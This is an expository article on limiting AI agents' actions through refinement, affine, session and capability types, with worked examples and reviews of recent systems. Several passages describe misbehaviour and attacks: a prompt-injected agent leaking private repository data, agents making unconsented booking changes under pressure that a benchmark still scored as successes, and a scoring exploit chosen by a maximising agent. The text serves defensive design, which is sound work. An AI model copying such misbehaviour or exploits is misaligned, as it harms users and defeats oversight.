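# Type-Theoretic Constraints on AI Agents: Refinement Types, Bounded Adaptation and Provable Safety

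## Types, refinement types and what a type checker proves

An AI agent is a software system that observes its surroundings and chooses actions, such as sending a payment, deleting a file or steering a vehicle. Engineers can limit those actions with type-theoretic constraints, which they write in a programming language's type system. The type system sorts values into kinds and fixes which operations apply to each kind. Before the agent's code runs, a type checker reads it and rejects it unless the checker can establish that the limits hold. Programming language researchers developed this technique decades before today's agents, for programs that people write by hand, and its guarantees and gaps are easiest to see in those programs.

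### Types and soundness

A type describes a set of values and the operations that make sense on them. The type `int` covers whole numbers, which a program can add or compare, and `string` covers text, which it can join or search. Functions also have types, so a function of type `int → int` takes a whole number and returns a whole number. A type checker computes the type of each expression from the types of its parts and stops with an error if the parts do not fit together, for instance if the code multiplies a name by a date. It does this without running the program, so a single check covers every input the program could receive, while a test covers only the inputs someone chose to try.

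The claim about every input needs its own proof, which covers the type system as a whole. The textbook *Practical Foundations for Programming Languages* gives the standard form, a type safety theorem with two clauses. In the theorem, e : τ means "expression e has type τ", and e ↦ e′ means "one step of execution turns e into e′".

- Preservation: if e : τ and e ↦ e′, then e′ : τ.
- Progress: if e : τ, then either e is a finished value or some e′ exists with e ↦ e′.

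An expression is stuck if it is not a value but has no next step. For example, an expression that adds a number to a piece of text is stuck. A well-typed program is not stuck at the start, by progress. It keeps its type after each step, by preservation, so progress applies again after every step for as long as the program runs. Well-typedness is therefore an invariant, a condition that holds at the start and that every step preserves.

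This guarantee covers only programs that are well typed in their entirety, not programs that mix in unchecked code. *A Logical Approach to Type Soundness* (Timany, Krebbers and colleagues, 2024) calls it "a rather weak theorem" for this reason. Ordinary types are also coarse. The type `int`, for example, rules out text but does not distinguish one integer from another. A well-typed program can still divide by zero, read past the end of an array, store 31 February as a date or return an unsorted list from a sorting routine (Jhala and Vazou, *Refinement Types*, 2020).

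### Refinement types, step by step

A refinement type is an ordinary type with a logical condition attached. The type `(v : int | 0 ≤ v)` contains exactly those integers v that are at least zero. Suppose a program pays money out of an account through one function, `spend`, which takes a balance b and an amount x and returns what is left:

```
spend : (b : int | 0 ≤ b) → (x : int | 0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ b) → (v : int | 0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ b)
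spend(b, x) = b − x
```

The symbol ∧ means "and", and v names the result. The condition on x includes b, so the permitted amount depends on the balance. With ordinary types the signature would be `int → int → int`, and `spend(100, 120)` would pass the checker and return −20.

Type checking relies on subtyping. A type S is a subtype of a type T when every value of S is also a value of T, so a program can use an S wherever it needs a T. One refinement of a base type is a subtype of another when its condition implies the other's, so `(v : int | p)` is a subtype of `(v : int | q)` when p implies q for every v. For example, the positive integers are a subtype of the non-negative integers because 0 < v implies 0 ≤ v. For function types, the direction reverses for inputs. A program can use a function that accepts all integers where it needs one that accepts non-negative integers, provided the function's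 results still fall within the required type.

Jhala and Vazou show how a checker turns this into a formula. The language supplies a precise type for subtraction: given m and n, the result is `(v : int | v = m − n)`. The body of `spend` therefore has the type `(v : int | v = b − x)`, while the signature requires `(v : int | 0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ b)`. The checker has to show that the type of the body is a subtype of the required one, and it may use the conditions on b and x as hypotheses. The result is a single formula, the verification condition:

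```
∀b. 0 ≤ b  ⇒  ∀x. (0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ b)  ⇒  ∀v. v = b − x  ⇒  (0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ b)
```

For every non-negative balance b and every amount x between 0 and b, if v equals b − x, then v lies between 0 and b.

The checker passes the formula to an SMT solver, a program that automatically decides whether logical formulas over numbers and data structures can be satisfied. To prove that p implies q, the solver searches for a counterexample, meaning values that satisfy p ∧ ¬q. Here a counterexample must satisfy 0 ≤ b, 0 ≤ x ≤ b and v = b − x, together with either v < 0 or v > b. If v < 0, then x is greater than b, which contradicts x ≤ b. If v > b, then x is negative, which contradicts 0 ≤ x. No counterexample exists, so the formula is valid and the checker accepts the function. Both halves of the condition on x are needed. Without 0 ≤ x, for example, a payment of −500 would raise the balance.

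Calls go through the same procedure. For `spend(100, 120)` the checker must show that the argument 120 belongs to the type of x with b set to 100:

```
∀v. v = 120  ⇒  (0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ 100)
```

The solver finds the counterexample v = 120, and the checker rejects the program before any of it has run.

A checker works out the result of a call from the function's signature and ignores the body, which makes checking modular but less precise. Suppose a program spends 30 out of 100, names the remainder c, and then calls `spend(c, 60)`. At run time c is 70, so the call is safe. But the signature of `spend` guarantees only 0 ≤ c ≤ 100, so the solver finds the counterexample c = 59 and the checker rejects the program. If the programmer strengthens the result condition to v = b − x, the same program passes.

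A sound checker never accepts a program that breaks the stated rule, and a complete checker never rejects a program that obeys it. Refinement type checkers aim for soundness and give up completeness, since no checker that always finishes can have both for all programs in a general-purpose language. *Refinement Reflection* (2016) replaces true containment between types with a conservative test by an SMT solver and proves that the replacement is sound. Jhala and Vazou restrict the conditions further, to a logic in which the solver always reaches a definite answer. This logic allows sums and comparisons of integers, and functions about which the solver may assume only that equal inputs give equal outputs, but it excludes "for all" inside a condition. The verification languages Dafny and F\* permit "for all" and so can express more, but the outcome of a check may then depend on the solver's heuristics.

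A proof of this kind also assumes that the built-in operations satisfy the types the language gives them. Machine arithmetic can violate this assumption, because adding one to the largest machine integer wraps round to a smaller number. *To Zip Through the Cost Analysis of Probabilistic Programs* (2025) notes that Liquid Haskell, a refinement checker for Haskell, translates machine integers into unbounded ones. This wrapping cannot affect `spend`, because b − x never leaves the range from 0 to b, but a `deposit` function that returns b + x could produce a negative balance on a real machine despite a valid proof. A stricter type for addition that requires the sum to fit in a machine integer prevents this.

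A type checker's proof also assumes that the type system itself is sound. Borkowski, Vazou and Jhala (2022), in *Mechanizing Refinement Types*, report that practical tools had developed far beyond what the theory covered. Naively combining subtyping with type variables, the placeholders that let one function work on many types, is unsound because contradictory conditions can disappear when a concrete type replaces the variable.

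### Values from outside the program

The amounts in the calls above were written in the program. An amount that comes from a user, a web page or a language model is not, and its type is plain `int`. If the code reads x from such a source and calls `spend(b, x)` directly, the checker has to prove 0 ≤ x ≤ b for every integer x. The solver finds the counterexample x = −1, so the checker rejects the program, even if every amount the program would actually receive is reasonable.

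The remedy is a test at run time:

```
let x = read_input() in
if 0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ b then spend(b, x) else b
```

When a checker reaches a conditional, it checks the `then` branch with the tested condition as an extra hypothesis and the `else` branch with the negation of that condition. For the call inside the `then` branch, the formula is now:

```
∀b. 0 ≤ b  ⇒  ∀x. (0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ b)  ⇒  ∀v. v = x  ⇒  (0 ≤ v ∧ v ≤ b)
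```

This is valid. The proof needs the hypothesis v = x because the test establishes a fact about x, while the call requires a fact about its argument v. Jhala and Vazou need the same link to verify a function that returns absolute values. *AeonBox*, Fonseca's proposal to confine AI agents with refinement types, gives an equally small example in a language called Aeon. Division accepts only a non-zero divisor, so a program that divides by a number it has just read does not compile until the programmer adds a branch for zero.

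Before the program runs, the checker proves that every path to `spend` goes through the test. While the program runs, the test compares the actual amount, which the checker never had, with the balance. The proof therefore holds wherever the amount comes from. If the amount is mistaken or chosen maliciously, either it fails the test and no money moves, or it passes and is within the balance. Most proposals for typed control of learned components depend on this step, because it means nobody has to prove anything about how the component arrived at the number. However, the condition must be something a program can compute, such as x ≤ b, which excludes conditions such as whether the account holder would have wanted the payment.

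### Between simple types and dependent types

Dependent types are more expressive than refinement types. They can depend on arbitrary values, and a proposition can be a type whose members are its proofs. In a dependently typed language such as Lean, `spend` could take a third argument, a proof that x ≤ b. To spend 30 out of 100, a caller supplies a proof of 30 ≤ 100. Nobody can call it with 100 and 120, because the type "120 ≤ 100" has no members.

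| | Simple types | Refinement types | Dependent types |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the type of `spend` can express | Two integers in, one integer out | The amount is within the balance; the result lies between 0 and b | Any mathematical statement about `spend`, including statements about whole histories of payments |
| Source of the proof | The checker alone | The checker and an SMT solver, working from conditions the programmer wrote | A person or a program writes the proof, often with automated help, and the checker verifies it |
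| Main cost | Little beyond ordinary programming | Precise signatures, and repairs where the solver fails | The proofs themselves, which can be longer than the code |

The boundaries between the columns are not sharp. Jhala and Vazou describe refinements as a knob that a programmer can turn from "no division by zero" up to full correctness, and Liquid Haskell lets the programmer write proofs as ordinary Haskell functions. *To Zip Through the Cost Analysis of Probabilistic Programs* classes Liquid Haskell as "auto-active", meaning that the programmer supplies code, conditions and hints in advance, and the tool then succeeds or fails without further input. Fonseca argues that this makes refinement types suitable for agents, since with Lean a person or the agent has to produce each proof explicitly, which takes time or generated text. The argument is reasonable, though he calls his own comparison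 of power and effort unscientific.

Even the less demanding option takes programmers considerable effort. Oliveira and Mendes (2025), in *What Challenges Do Developers Face When Using Verification-Aware Programming Languages?*, applied topic modelling to developers' discussions on public forums and found that steep learning curves and poor usability were among the main obstacles. People tend to post on forums when they are stuck, so the study is better evidence of what the difficulties are than of how common they are.

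All the types so far describe values. The function `spend` computes a number, and no money moves until some other code contacts a bank. An effect type records what a computation may do to the outside world, such as write files or use the network. A function's effects include those of any function it calls. Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, models a program's effects as a set of pairs, each containing a kind of effect and its argument, such as network access and the target host. The set is sound if it includes every effect the program can produce in any run on any input, even if it also includes effects that never occur. A related device is the capability, an unforgeable program value that permits the code holding it to produce particular effects. Code that holds no network capability cannot use the network. If types record which capabilities a function holds,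 a reader or a checker can see from its signature the most that the function could do. Language designers have begun to apply this approach to code that agents write.

### Safety, liveness and termination

Computer scientists divide the properties of a running program into safety, "nothing bad happens", and liveness, "something good eventually happens". "The balance never falls below zero" is a safety property, and a single moment with a negative balance violates it. "Every approved invoice is eventually paid" is a liveness property, which no finite delay can refute because the payment might still come. The type of `spend` expresses only safety, so a program that never pays anybody satisfies it.

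A similar distinction applies to single functions. Partial correctness means that if the function returns, its result meets the specification. Total correctness adds that the function does return. Suppose a careless programmer defines `spend` by having it call itself:

```
spend(b, x) = spend(b, x)
```

Jhala and Vazou's rule for recursion lets the checker assume that `spend` has its declared type while checking the body. Under that assumption the body returns a value between 0 and b, so the definition passes, even though `spend` loops forever. The checker is still correct, because the type restricts only the balance that `spend` returns, and `spend` never returns. To prove termination, the programmer has to identify a quantity that shrinks with each call and cannot shrink indefinitely.

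In some languages, termination also matters for safety. The type `(v : int | false)` has no values, but a computation that loops forever can have this type. The checker then assumes "false" when it checks the code that follows, and anything can be proved from false, including 120 ≤ 100. Haskell evaluates lazily, computing a value only when something needs it, so the code that follows may run without the loop ever running. *Refinement Reflection* therefore requires Liquid Haskell to track which computations provably terminate. In a language that finishes each step before starting the next, the false assumption is harmless because the loop keeps the code after it from running.

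### From 1991 to Scala 3

The idea of attaching conditions to types goes back at least to Robert Cartwright's work on Lisp in 1976. Tim Freeman and Frank Pfenning introduced the name "refinement types" in 1991. Clancy's *Refinement Types, Annotated Bibliography* describes their system as addressing a problem in the language ML. The compiler warned of missing cases even when a programmer had handled every case that could occur at that point in the code, because it could not determine that the others were impossible there. Freeman and Pfenning let programmers divide a data type into named subsets, such as empty and non-empty lists. Their system had no arithmetic, but in 1998 Hongwei Xi and Pfenning added integer constraints, which allowed checks on array bounds. In the same year, John Rushby and colleagues introduced the form of subtyping by logical condition that present systems rely on.

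Programmers still had to write conditions everywhere. Liquid Types, which Patrick Rondon and colleagues published in 2008, reduced this work through inference. In Jhala and Vazou's account, the programmer may leave a condition blank. The checker puts an unknown κ in its place, generates the usual formulas with κ in them, and searches for a condition that makes them all valid. Liquid Haskell later brought this approach to Haskell. In another line of work, aimed at security, *Refinement Types for Secure Implementations* (2010) used conditions to express authorization policies (rules about who may do what) for F# programs. F\*, a successor to that work, has been used to verify cryptographic code in widely used web browsers.

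In most of these systems the conditions live outside the host language. A Liquid Haskell user writes them in special comments for a separate tool to read, and one participant in a usability study compared the experience to doing two things at once. Bovel, Kunčak and Odersky (2026), in *First-Class Refinement Types for Scala*, instead build refinements into the compiler of Scala 3, a widely used general-purpose language. In their syntax the example becomes:

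```
def spend(b: Int with b >= 0, x: Int with 0 <= x && x <= b): {v: Int with v == b - x} = b - x
```

Each condition is part of an ordinary Scala type, so the compiler's existing inference and subtyping rules apply to it. When the compiler cannot prove a condition, the programmer can match a value against the refined type, with one branch for success and one for failure, or write `.runtimeChecked`, which tests the value and throws an exception if the test fails. Conditions may not refer to mutable variables, because a later assignment could make a proven condition false. This restriction protects only values inside the program. If another process withdraws money from the real account after the program has read b, the proof still holds for b, but b is out of date.

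Bovel and colleagues proved soundness for a small core language and checked the proof with the proof assistant Rocq. The core language has an interpreter with a limited supply of "fuel", and a run ends when the fuel runs out, the program gets stuck, or it yields a value. The proof defines each type by the values that belong to it. A value belongs to a refinement type if it belongs to the base type and the condition, when executed on it, returns true or never finishes. They proved that a well-typed program never gets stuck and that, if it finishes, its result belongs to its type. This is partial correctness, so the programmer does not have to prove termination. People wrote the theorem statements, while AI tools, chiefly Claude Code, helped to generate many of the proofs. This does not weaken the result, because Rocq checks every proof in the same way, and it reduces the effort that has long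 been a drawback of dependent types.

On the team's benchmarks, checking added between 0 and 12 per cent to compilation time. An earlier refinement checker for Scala added 20 to 38 per cent, and the verifier Stainless added at least 56. The prototype is faster partly because it replaces the SMT solver with a weaker one, about 600 lines of code that simplify expressions and track which of them are equal. The soundness proof does not cover this code. It defines what it means for one condition to imply another, and assumes that the solver correctly decides when this is so. The solver also assumes that every function in a condition terminates and has no side effects, and a condition with side effects produces an error without any warning. The solver has no decision procedure for linear arithmetic either. It can confirm that `spend` returns b − x, because the body is that expression, but it cannot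 derive 0 ≤ b − x from x ≤ b. For now, a programmer who wants the type to guarantee a non-negative balance would have to test the result at run time.

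## Writing an agent's goals and limits as types

The `spend` function limits one number in one call. Developers also want to limit which tools an agent may use, how much it spends over a whole session, the order of its steps and what it does with private data. They can write all of these limits as types, but the checker can verify only some of them before the program runs and has to leave the others to run-time tests.

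### Limits

A precondition on an action is a refinement of the action's input, as in `spend`. Metere applies the idea to the envelope, the structured message in which a language model requests a tool call. Let D be the set of permissions that a developer has declared for the agent:

```
dispatch : (e : Envelope | permission(e) ∈ D) → Result
```

As with an outside amount in `spend`, the program has to test the envelope before it calls `dispatch`.

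A budget covers many calls, and each call has to leave less for the next:

```
charge : Budget(n) → (x : int | 0 ≤ x ∧ x ≤ n) → Budget(n − x)
```

This works only if the program cannot keep the old budget and spend it again. An affine type prevents that because the checker lets a program use such a value at most once. *Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) documents 63 incidents in which agents overran their budgets, and presents a budget library written in Rust, a language whose compiler already tracks ownership in this way. The compiler rejects any program that copies a budget, spends it twice or uses it after handing it to a sub-agent. The library enforces the cap itself at run time, by subtracting each call's estimated cost from the budget and refusing calls that would exceed the remainder.

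For a single agent, a four-line Python counter enforced the cap just as well. The types mattered when an agent delegated to several sub-agents in parallel. Careless Python code overspent in all 30 trials, while the Rust compiler rejected the same pattern. A Python counter with proper locking never overspent, so the types protect against programmer mistakes but do not make the cap any tighter. Khan's guarantee excludes reasoning models, because providers bill for hidden reasoning that the estimate does not bound.

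An invariant on state appears on both sides of the arrow:

```
step : (s : State | spent(s) ≤ cap) → Action → (t : State | spent(t) ≤ cap)
```

`step` must return a permitted state for every action, so its body has to reject forbidden actions, for example by returning `s` unchanged. The type covers only state changes made through `step`.

For the order of steps, programming language researchers developed typestate, in which the operations available on an object depend on its current state, and session types, which describe the sequence of messages between parties. A refund might need an identity check first and a human decision afterwards:

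```
verify  : Session(start) → UserId → Session(verified) + Session(denied)
propose : Session(verified) → Amount → Session(awaiting_approval)
```

The plus sign means "one or the other". A program that calls `propose` on a session in the state `start` does not compile.

A compiler cannot check a language model, so Sikaroudi's *Concordat* (2026) enforces such protocols at run time. On each turn, the Python library offers the model only the tools that are legal in the current state, and it rejects any other call before it takes effect. When a developer defines an agent, the library checks that every state can reach a final state, so that the agent cannot get stuck halfway. At this stage it also rejects a derived agent that bypasses its parent's protocol, such as a "fast refund" agent that jumps straight to `refunded`.

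Sikaroudi tested the library on 50 airline customer-service tasks. The airline's policy requires an explicit "yes" from the customer before any change to a booking, and he instructed the simulated customers to push back the first time the agent asked for one. When the rule was only in the prompt, an agent running gpt-4.1 made unconfirmed changes in 13 of the 50 tasks, and one running Claude Haiku 5.5 did so in 29 of 128 runs. Agents restricted by the protocol made none, and the differences in task success were not statistically significant. The absence of violations follows from the design, because the library and the scoring used the same test for a "yes". The main finding is that the unrestricted agents broke the rule, which they did only when customers pushed back. When the customers cooperated, the unrestricted Haiku agent confirmed every change.

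Types can also record where data came from. In Fonseca's AeonBox, a session becomes tainted once the agent has read a private code repository:

```
readRepo    : (s : Session) → (r : Repo) → (t : Session | tainted(t) = (private(r) ∨ tainted(s)))
createIssue : (s : Session | ¬tainted(s)) → (r : Repo | ¬private(r)) → Text → Issue
```

The symbol ∨ means "or" and ¬ means "not". A program that reads a private repository and then posts publicly fails the check, whatever instructions the model found on a web page. Sessions are linear, so the program must use each one exactly once and cannot go back to an older, untainted session.

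Developers already enforce many such limits, usually without any special types. *When Code Becomes an LLM Call* (2026) examined 5,017 constraints that developers had implemented around calls to language models. Programs enforced 78 per cent of them, mostly through checks in code. Code cannot check some of the others, such as a request to reason carefully, but it could check many of them. For example, one trading system asks its model for at most eight indicators with exact names, but its code checks only that the reply contains a tool call.

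### A plan whose type contains its goal

An agent that does nothing obeys every limit above. To write down what the agent should achieve, programmers can draw on AI planning, a field that has treated goals as logical conditions since the 1970s. A planner takes a description of the world, a list of possible actions and a goal, and searches for a sequence of actions that reaches the goal. Hill, Komendantskaya and colleagues (2021), in *Actions You Can Handle*, translate such plans into Agda, a dependently typed language, where a valid plan is a program of this type:

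```
plan : initialWorld ⇝ goalState
```

A world is a list of facts, such as "taxi 1 is at location 1". A goal is a list of facts that must be true or must be false at the end. Two rules determine which plans have the type:

- The empty plan has type w ⇝ g if the world w satisfies the goal g.
- A plan that begins with action α and continues with plan f has type w ⇝ g if w satisfies the preconditions of α and f has type w′ ⇝ g, where w′ is w after the effects of α.

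In their example, taxis 1, 2 and 3 and persons 1, 2 and 3 start at locations 1, 2 and 3 respectively. The goal is to have taxi 1 at location 2, person 1 at location 3 and person 3 at location 1. The checker goes through the plan like this:

| Step | What must hold | What changes |
|---|---|---|
| Taxi 3 drives person 3 from 3 to 1 | Taxi 3 and person 3 are at 3 | Both are now at 1 |
| Taxi 1 drives from 1 to 2 | Taxi 1 is at 1 | Taxi 1 is now at 2 |
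| Taxi 3 drives person 1 from 1 to 3 | Taxi 3 and person 1 are at 1 | Both are now at 3 |
| Stop | Taxi 1 is at 2, person 1 at 3, person 3 at 1 | Nothing |

If the first and third steps are swapped, taxi 3 is not at location 1 when it has to be, and the plan no longer has the type. In earlier work the group proved the rules sound, so executing a plan of type w ⇝ g from the world w ends in a world that satisfies g. Because a plan is a finite list, the result also covers liveness, meaning that the agent reaches the goal and stops.

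However, the theorem is only about the described world, and the description rests on strong assumptions. Any fact missing from the list counts as false, and every action has exactly its listed effects and changes nothing else. For example, a taxi in this model can always drive from one location to another, because nothing in the type covers closed roads.

A goal of this kind also does not constrain anything it leaves out. Suppose we add a fourth step to the plan, in which taxi 2 drives person 2 to location 3. The longer plan has the same type as the original because person 2 is not part of the goal. Adding "person 2 is at location 2" to the goal would exclude that plan, but not one that takes person 2 on a long detour and back. Excluding the detour requires a condition on every state along the way, which later versions of the standard planning language allow. The airline tests had the same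 problem. In Sikaroudi's first run with Haiku under pressure, the benchmark gave full marks to 8 of the 13 tasks in which the agent had changed a booking without consent, because the final database was correct.

Hill and colleagues add further conditions at the point where a program executes the plan. For fuel, they change the type of the function that carries out an action:

```
Action → World × Fuel(n + 1) → World × Fuel(n)
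```

Nobody can call this function with an empty tank, since no number n makes n + 1 equal to zero. The program checks the level before each action and returns an error if the tank is empty. For simplicity, every action uses one unit of fuel. A real taxi would need to measure its fuel instead of counting units.

Their other example is fairness between male and female taxi drivers, which basic planning languages cannot express. Their formula for it requires each gender's share of passenger trips to be at least its share of the drivers, less a margin, but only once the total number of trips reaches ten times the number of drivers. The program executes an action only if it can construct a proof that the action satisfies the formula. The proof is rigorous, but the formula ignores the length and pay of trips, so a company could satisfy it while giving women all the short trips.

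### Goals to reach and quantities to maximise

The taxi goal is a predicate, which a plan either satisfies or fails. Economists and machine learning researchers more often describe a goal as a quantity to maximise. Suppose a function f predicts the outcome of each action in a set A, and u gives each outcome a score. Both kinds of goal then fit into a refinement type:

```
reach    : (a : A | goal(f(a)))
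maximise : (a : A | ∀c : A. u(f(c)) ≤ u(f(a)))
```

Checking `reach` involves only the chosen action, but checking `maximise` means comparing that action with every alternative. This requires a "for all" condition, which SMT solvers handle less reliably. If every action has a better alternative, the `maximise` type has no members.

Suppose three actions score 70, 85 and 90. The second and third both meet a goal of scoring at least 80, but only the third meets a goal of achieving the maximum score. Now suppose a new tool lets the agent score 95 by exploiting an error in the scoring. The old proofs for `reach` remain valid, but the proof that 90 is the maximum fails, and the exploit becomes the only action of the type that requires the maximum. A designer can restrict the comparison to actions that meet a safety condition, but that condition has to exclude every exploit in advance. This is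 a practical reason to prefer thresholds for an agent whose abilities may grow, although it means accepting results that are good enough rather than the best available.

Researchers in agent foundations, the mathematical study of what agents are, use types to describe agency itself. Scott Garrabrant's post *(A → B) → A* (2018) proposes its title as the "type of agency", where A stands for actions and B for outcomes. Garrabrant reads the arrows mainly as causes, so that an action happens because it leads to a certain outcome. The arrows can also be read as functions, in which case an agent takes a prediction of each action's outcome and returns an action. One example is argmax, which returns the input at which a function is largest.

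The signature (A → B) → A describes how an agent is built but leaves its preferences open. Take two actions, pay and wait, and two outcomes, settled and unsettled. A prediction assigns an outcome to each action, so there are four possible predictions. A chooser assigns an action to each prediction, so there are 2⁴ = 16 choosers. One of them picks an action that settles the debt whenever the prediction includes one. Another avoids settling whenever it can, and a third always waits, whatever the prediction. All sixteen have the same type. The preferences are in the particular function, which, as *riffing on the agent type* (2022) puts it, "hardcodes its notion of utility."

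If there are at least two outcomes, any agent of this type must choose the same action for some different predictions, whatever the set of actions. For example, an agent with four possible predictions and only two actions must choose the same action for at least two of the predictions. Garrabrant describes such agents as "lossy".

Restricting what the agent may bring about takes a refinement:

```
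choose : (f : A → B | ∃a. safe(f(a))) → (a : A | safe(f(a)))
```

The symbol ∃ means "there is". Without the condition on f, nobody could write the function, because some predictions leave no safe action to return. A comment on Garrabrant's post points to a gap that remains even with this type. The refinement constrains only f(a), the outcome the agent aims at, while the actual outcome depends on how the world responds to a.

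### Two agents and one budget

Agents can each obey a limit and still break it together. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) gives an example with a shared budget of $100,000. Agent A can spend $45,000 or nothing, and agent B can spend $60,000 or nothing. Each sees only its own part of the system. If both read the balance before either pays, `spend(100000, 45000)` and `spend(100000, 60000)` both pass the type check, so the agents spend $105,000 in total. Each proof is correct for the balance its agent read. Database researchers described this kind of failure in 1995 and called it write skew.

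In Sterling's remedy, agents propose changes and a single adjudicator, which he calls the meta-agent, decides whether to accept them. Only the meta-agent can see and change the whole state. It is a checklist in ordinary code and does not call a language model. It takes proposals one at a time, computes the state that would result and tests that state against each invariant. Each test returns "pass", "reject" or "escalate", and the change takes effect only if every test passes. The meta-agent adds an entry to a permanent log either way.

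If A's proposal arrives first, it brings the total to $45,000 and the adjudicator approves it. B's proposal would then bring the total to $105,000, so the adjudicator rejects it. If B's proposal arrives first, the adjudicator approves it and rejects A's. The invariant limits the total but does not determine who should get the money.

Sterling proves that if the initial state satisfies the invariants, so does every state the system can reach, whatever the agents propose. A language model drafted about 90 per cent of the appendix with the formal proofs, and Sterling corrected errors in earlier versions, but the central argument can be followed without the appendix. Only the adjudicator can change the state, and it commits only states that satisfy the invariants, so if the invariants hold before a change, they hold after it. The argument fails if an agent has another way to pay, such as a company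 card. It also doesn't cover human decisions, because in the extended design a person who receives an escalated proposal may approve a change that violates an invariant.

Another solution is an affine budget. The owner can split the $100,000 in advance, say into $45,000 for A and $55,000 for B, so that neither agent can affect the other and no adjudicator is needed. This is less flexible, because B can then never make its $60,000 payment, even if A spends nothing. The adjudicator avoids this waste, but it has to handle changes one at a time.

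The invariants in Sterling's design come from an ontology, in which a human expert describes a field by listing the things in it, the processes they go through and the rules that apply. A language model then groups processes that use the same data into roles for agents, and turns rules and preconditions into invariants. His main case is billing for drug tests under Arizona's Medicaid programme. A patient with more than 90 days of abstinence may have three definitive tests in 90 days, while one with less than 30 days may have one every seven days. David, in the first group, has a definitive test on 23 March. On 26 March a quick screening test detects opioids, and his clinic orders another definitive test. The positive screen moves him to the second group, so the programme will not pay for another definitive test within seven days of the last. A billing agent that still has his old status on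 file would approve the claim.

The theorem guarantees the invariants as written, including any errors. Sterling's second case, the disclosure of security flaws, has nine invariants. One forbids publication until a patch has been released and an embargo has ended. Another requires a patch before publication unless the embargo has ended without one. Both must hold, so the exception has no effect as worded. If the vendor never releases a patch, the adjudicator would block publication for good under the first rule, unless the flaw is already public.

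### Bastion

The encodings so far limit individual calls or changes of state. Bastion, a proposed "operating system" for AI agents, would instead give each agent a small language that contains only permitted commands. Omar, Ferris and Madhavapeddy presented it in *Modularizing Reasoning about AI Capabilities via Abstract Dijkstra Monads* (2024), a talk at a conference on functional programming. Their example is an agent that carries out environmental projects and might alter sensor data to hide a loss of habitat, or reveal the location of rare animals to poachers. For file access, they propose an interface along these lines:

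```
CapDataAccess(readonly, writable):
  type Cmd a
  return    : a → Cmd a
  bind      : Cmd a → (a → Cmd b) → Cmd b
  readfile  : Path → Cmd string
  writefile : Path → string → Cmd ()
```

`Cmd a` is the type of commands that produce a value of type `a`. A type like this is called a monad when it has the operations `return`, which produces a value and does nothing else, and `bind`, which runs one command and passes its result to the next. `Cmd` is abstract, meaning that its implementation is hidden, so an agent can build commands only from the four listed operations. None of these operations sends data over the network, so no program the agent writes can do so.

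`writefile` accepts any path, and the restriction to writable directories is in the hidden implementation. Omar and colleagues intend to prove that implementation correct using Dijkstra monads, which attach a rule to each command. Given a condition that should hold after the command runs, the rule computes what must hold before it. Developers would do this proof once for each interface, and it would cover every program that an agent writes against that interface.

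The policy that assigns directories to agents starts from the organisation's access list and removes the directories that a second AI marks as unnecessary for the task. Because the second AI can only remove directories, it cannot widen the agent's access even if it is wrong or hostile, though it can make the task impossible by removing directories the task needs.

The most ambitious part of the proposal would require an agent to prove, before it acts, that an intervention is likely to have the intended effect. That depends on a detailed causal model of the world, which the researchers hoped many contributors would build together.

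The proofs were still only planned in 2024. In late November 2026, Omar's research page still listed Bastion with the 2024 talk and a 2014 workshop paper, but no later paper, proof or software. Fonseca's AeonBox comes closer to a working version of the idea. Its agent has no terminal access and reaches GitHub only through a typed library.

### A hard case: "do not deceive the user"

Suppose the owner of a refund agent wants it never to deceive a customer. Part of this is a condition on recorded events. The agent should say that a refund has gone through only if the payment system has recorded one:

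```
confirmRefund : (log : Log) → (r : Refund | succeeded(r) ∈ log) → Message
```

The same pattern covers any claim about a logged event, such as a claim that tests passed or that a person reviewed a decision. The function must compose the message from a template. If the agent can also write free text, it can make the same claim without the check, and catching that would require translating arbitrary sentences into logic.

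An agent can also mislead people with true statements. It might correctly tell a customer that it has submitted a refund request, but leave out that the company rejects nearly all such requests. Whether this is deception depends on what the customer comes to believe and, on many accounts, on what the agent intended, and the log contains neither. Philosophers also disagree about whether silence can be enough to deceive someone, and there is no agreed formal definition of intent for a language model. An engineer can pick a definition of deception and prove that the agent never deceives anyone by that definition, but the proof has the same weakness as the taxi company's fairness formula.

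Even consent, a simpler notion than deception, is hard to detect in a message. Sikaroudi's library treats any message that contains "yes", "yep" or "yeah" as consent, so it would accept "yes, but not that one" and reject "go ahead". For real use he recommends a button, because the company can then define consent as pressing it, and the log records whether the customer did. A button would not work for deception, because a deceived customer does not know that there is anything to report.

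## Type-checking the programs an agent writes

A compiler can check a program that a language model writes, although it cannot check the model itself. Several research groups have built agents in which the model writes a short program that can call several tools, instead of requesting the calls one at a time. The program runs only if the compiler accepts it.

### From request to running code

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, reduce the method to one Scala function:

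```
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

Here `task` is a request in plain English and `T` is the type of result that the surrounding program needs. A call to `agent` goes through four steps:

1. The model receives the task, the required type, the surrounding source code and a list of the variables and functions it may use.
2. It replies with Scala code.
3. The compiler checks the code as if a programmer had typed it at that point in the program.
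4. If the code fails, the model gets the error messages and tries again, up to a fixed number of attempts. If the code passes, it runs, and its result becomes the value of the call.

The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one of the team's examples, an account holds 100, and the model is asked to subtract 50 and return the new balance as an integer. It writes one line that subtracts 50 and another that returns a sentence containing the balance. The compiler rejects the code because a sentence is not an integer, so neither line runs and the balance stays at 100. An interpreter that finds type errors only as it reaches them would subtract 50 before finding the error, and a second attempt would subtract another 50.

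The type `Int` does not guarantee a correct answer, since code that subtracts 60 also type-checks. In most languages, it also does not stop the code from deleting files before returning the integer. To rule that out, the types have to cover effects. Two systems from 2026 do this. TACIT puts capabilities into Scala's types, and ELBA uses Haskell's effect types.

### TACIT: capabilities in types

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system designed for agents that work with secrets. For example, a company might want a cloud-hosted model to compare confidential contracts without the text reaching the model's provider. The team treats the model as a possible attacker because it may be hostile or may follow a prompt injection, an instruction that someone has planted in a file, email or web page for the agent to read.

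TACIT relies on capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3. Each type carries a capture set, which lists the capabilities that a value of the type may use. Suppose `f` is a capability to write to one particular file:

```
(s: String) => f.write(s)     // type: String ->{f} Unit
(s: String) => s.length       // type: String -> Int
```

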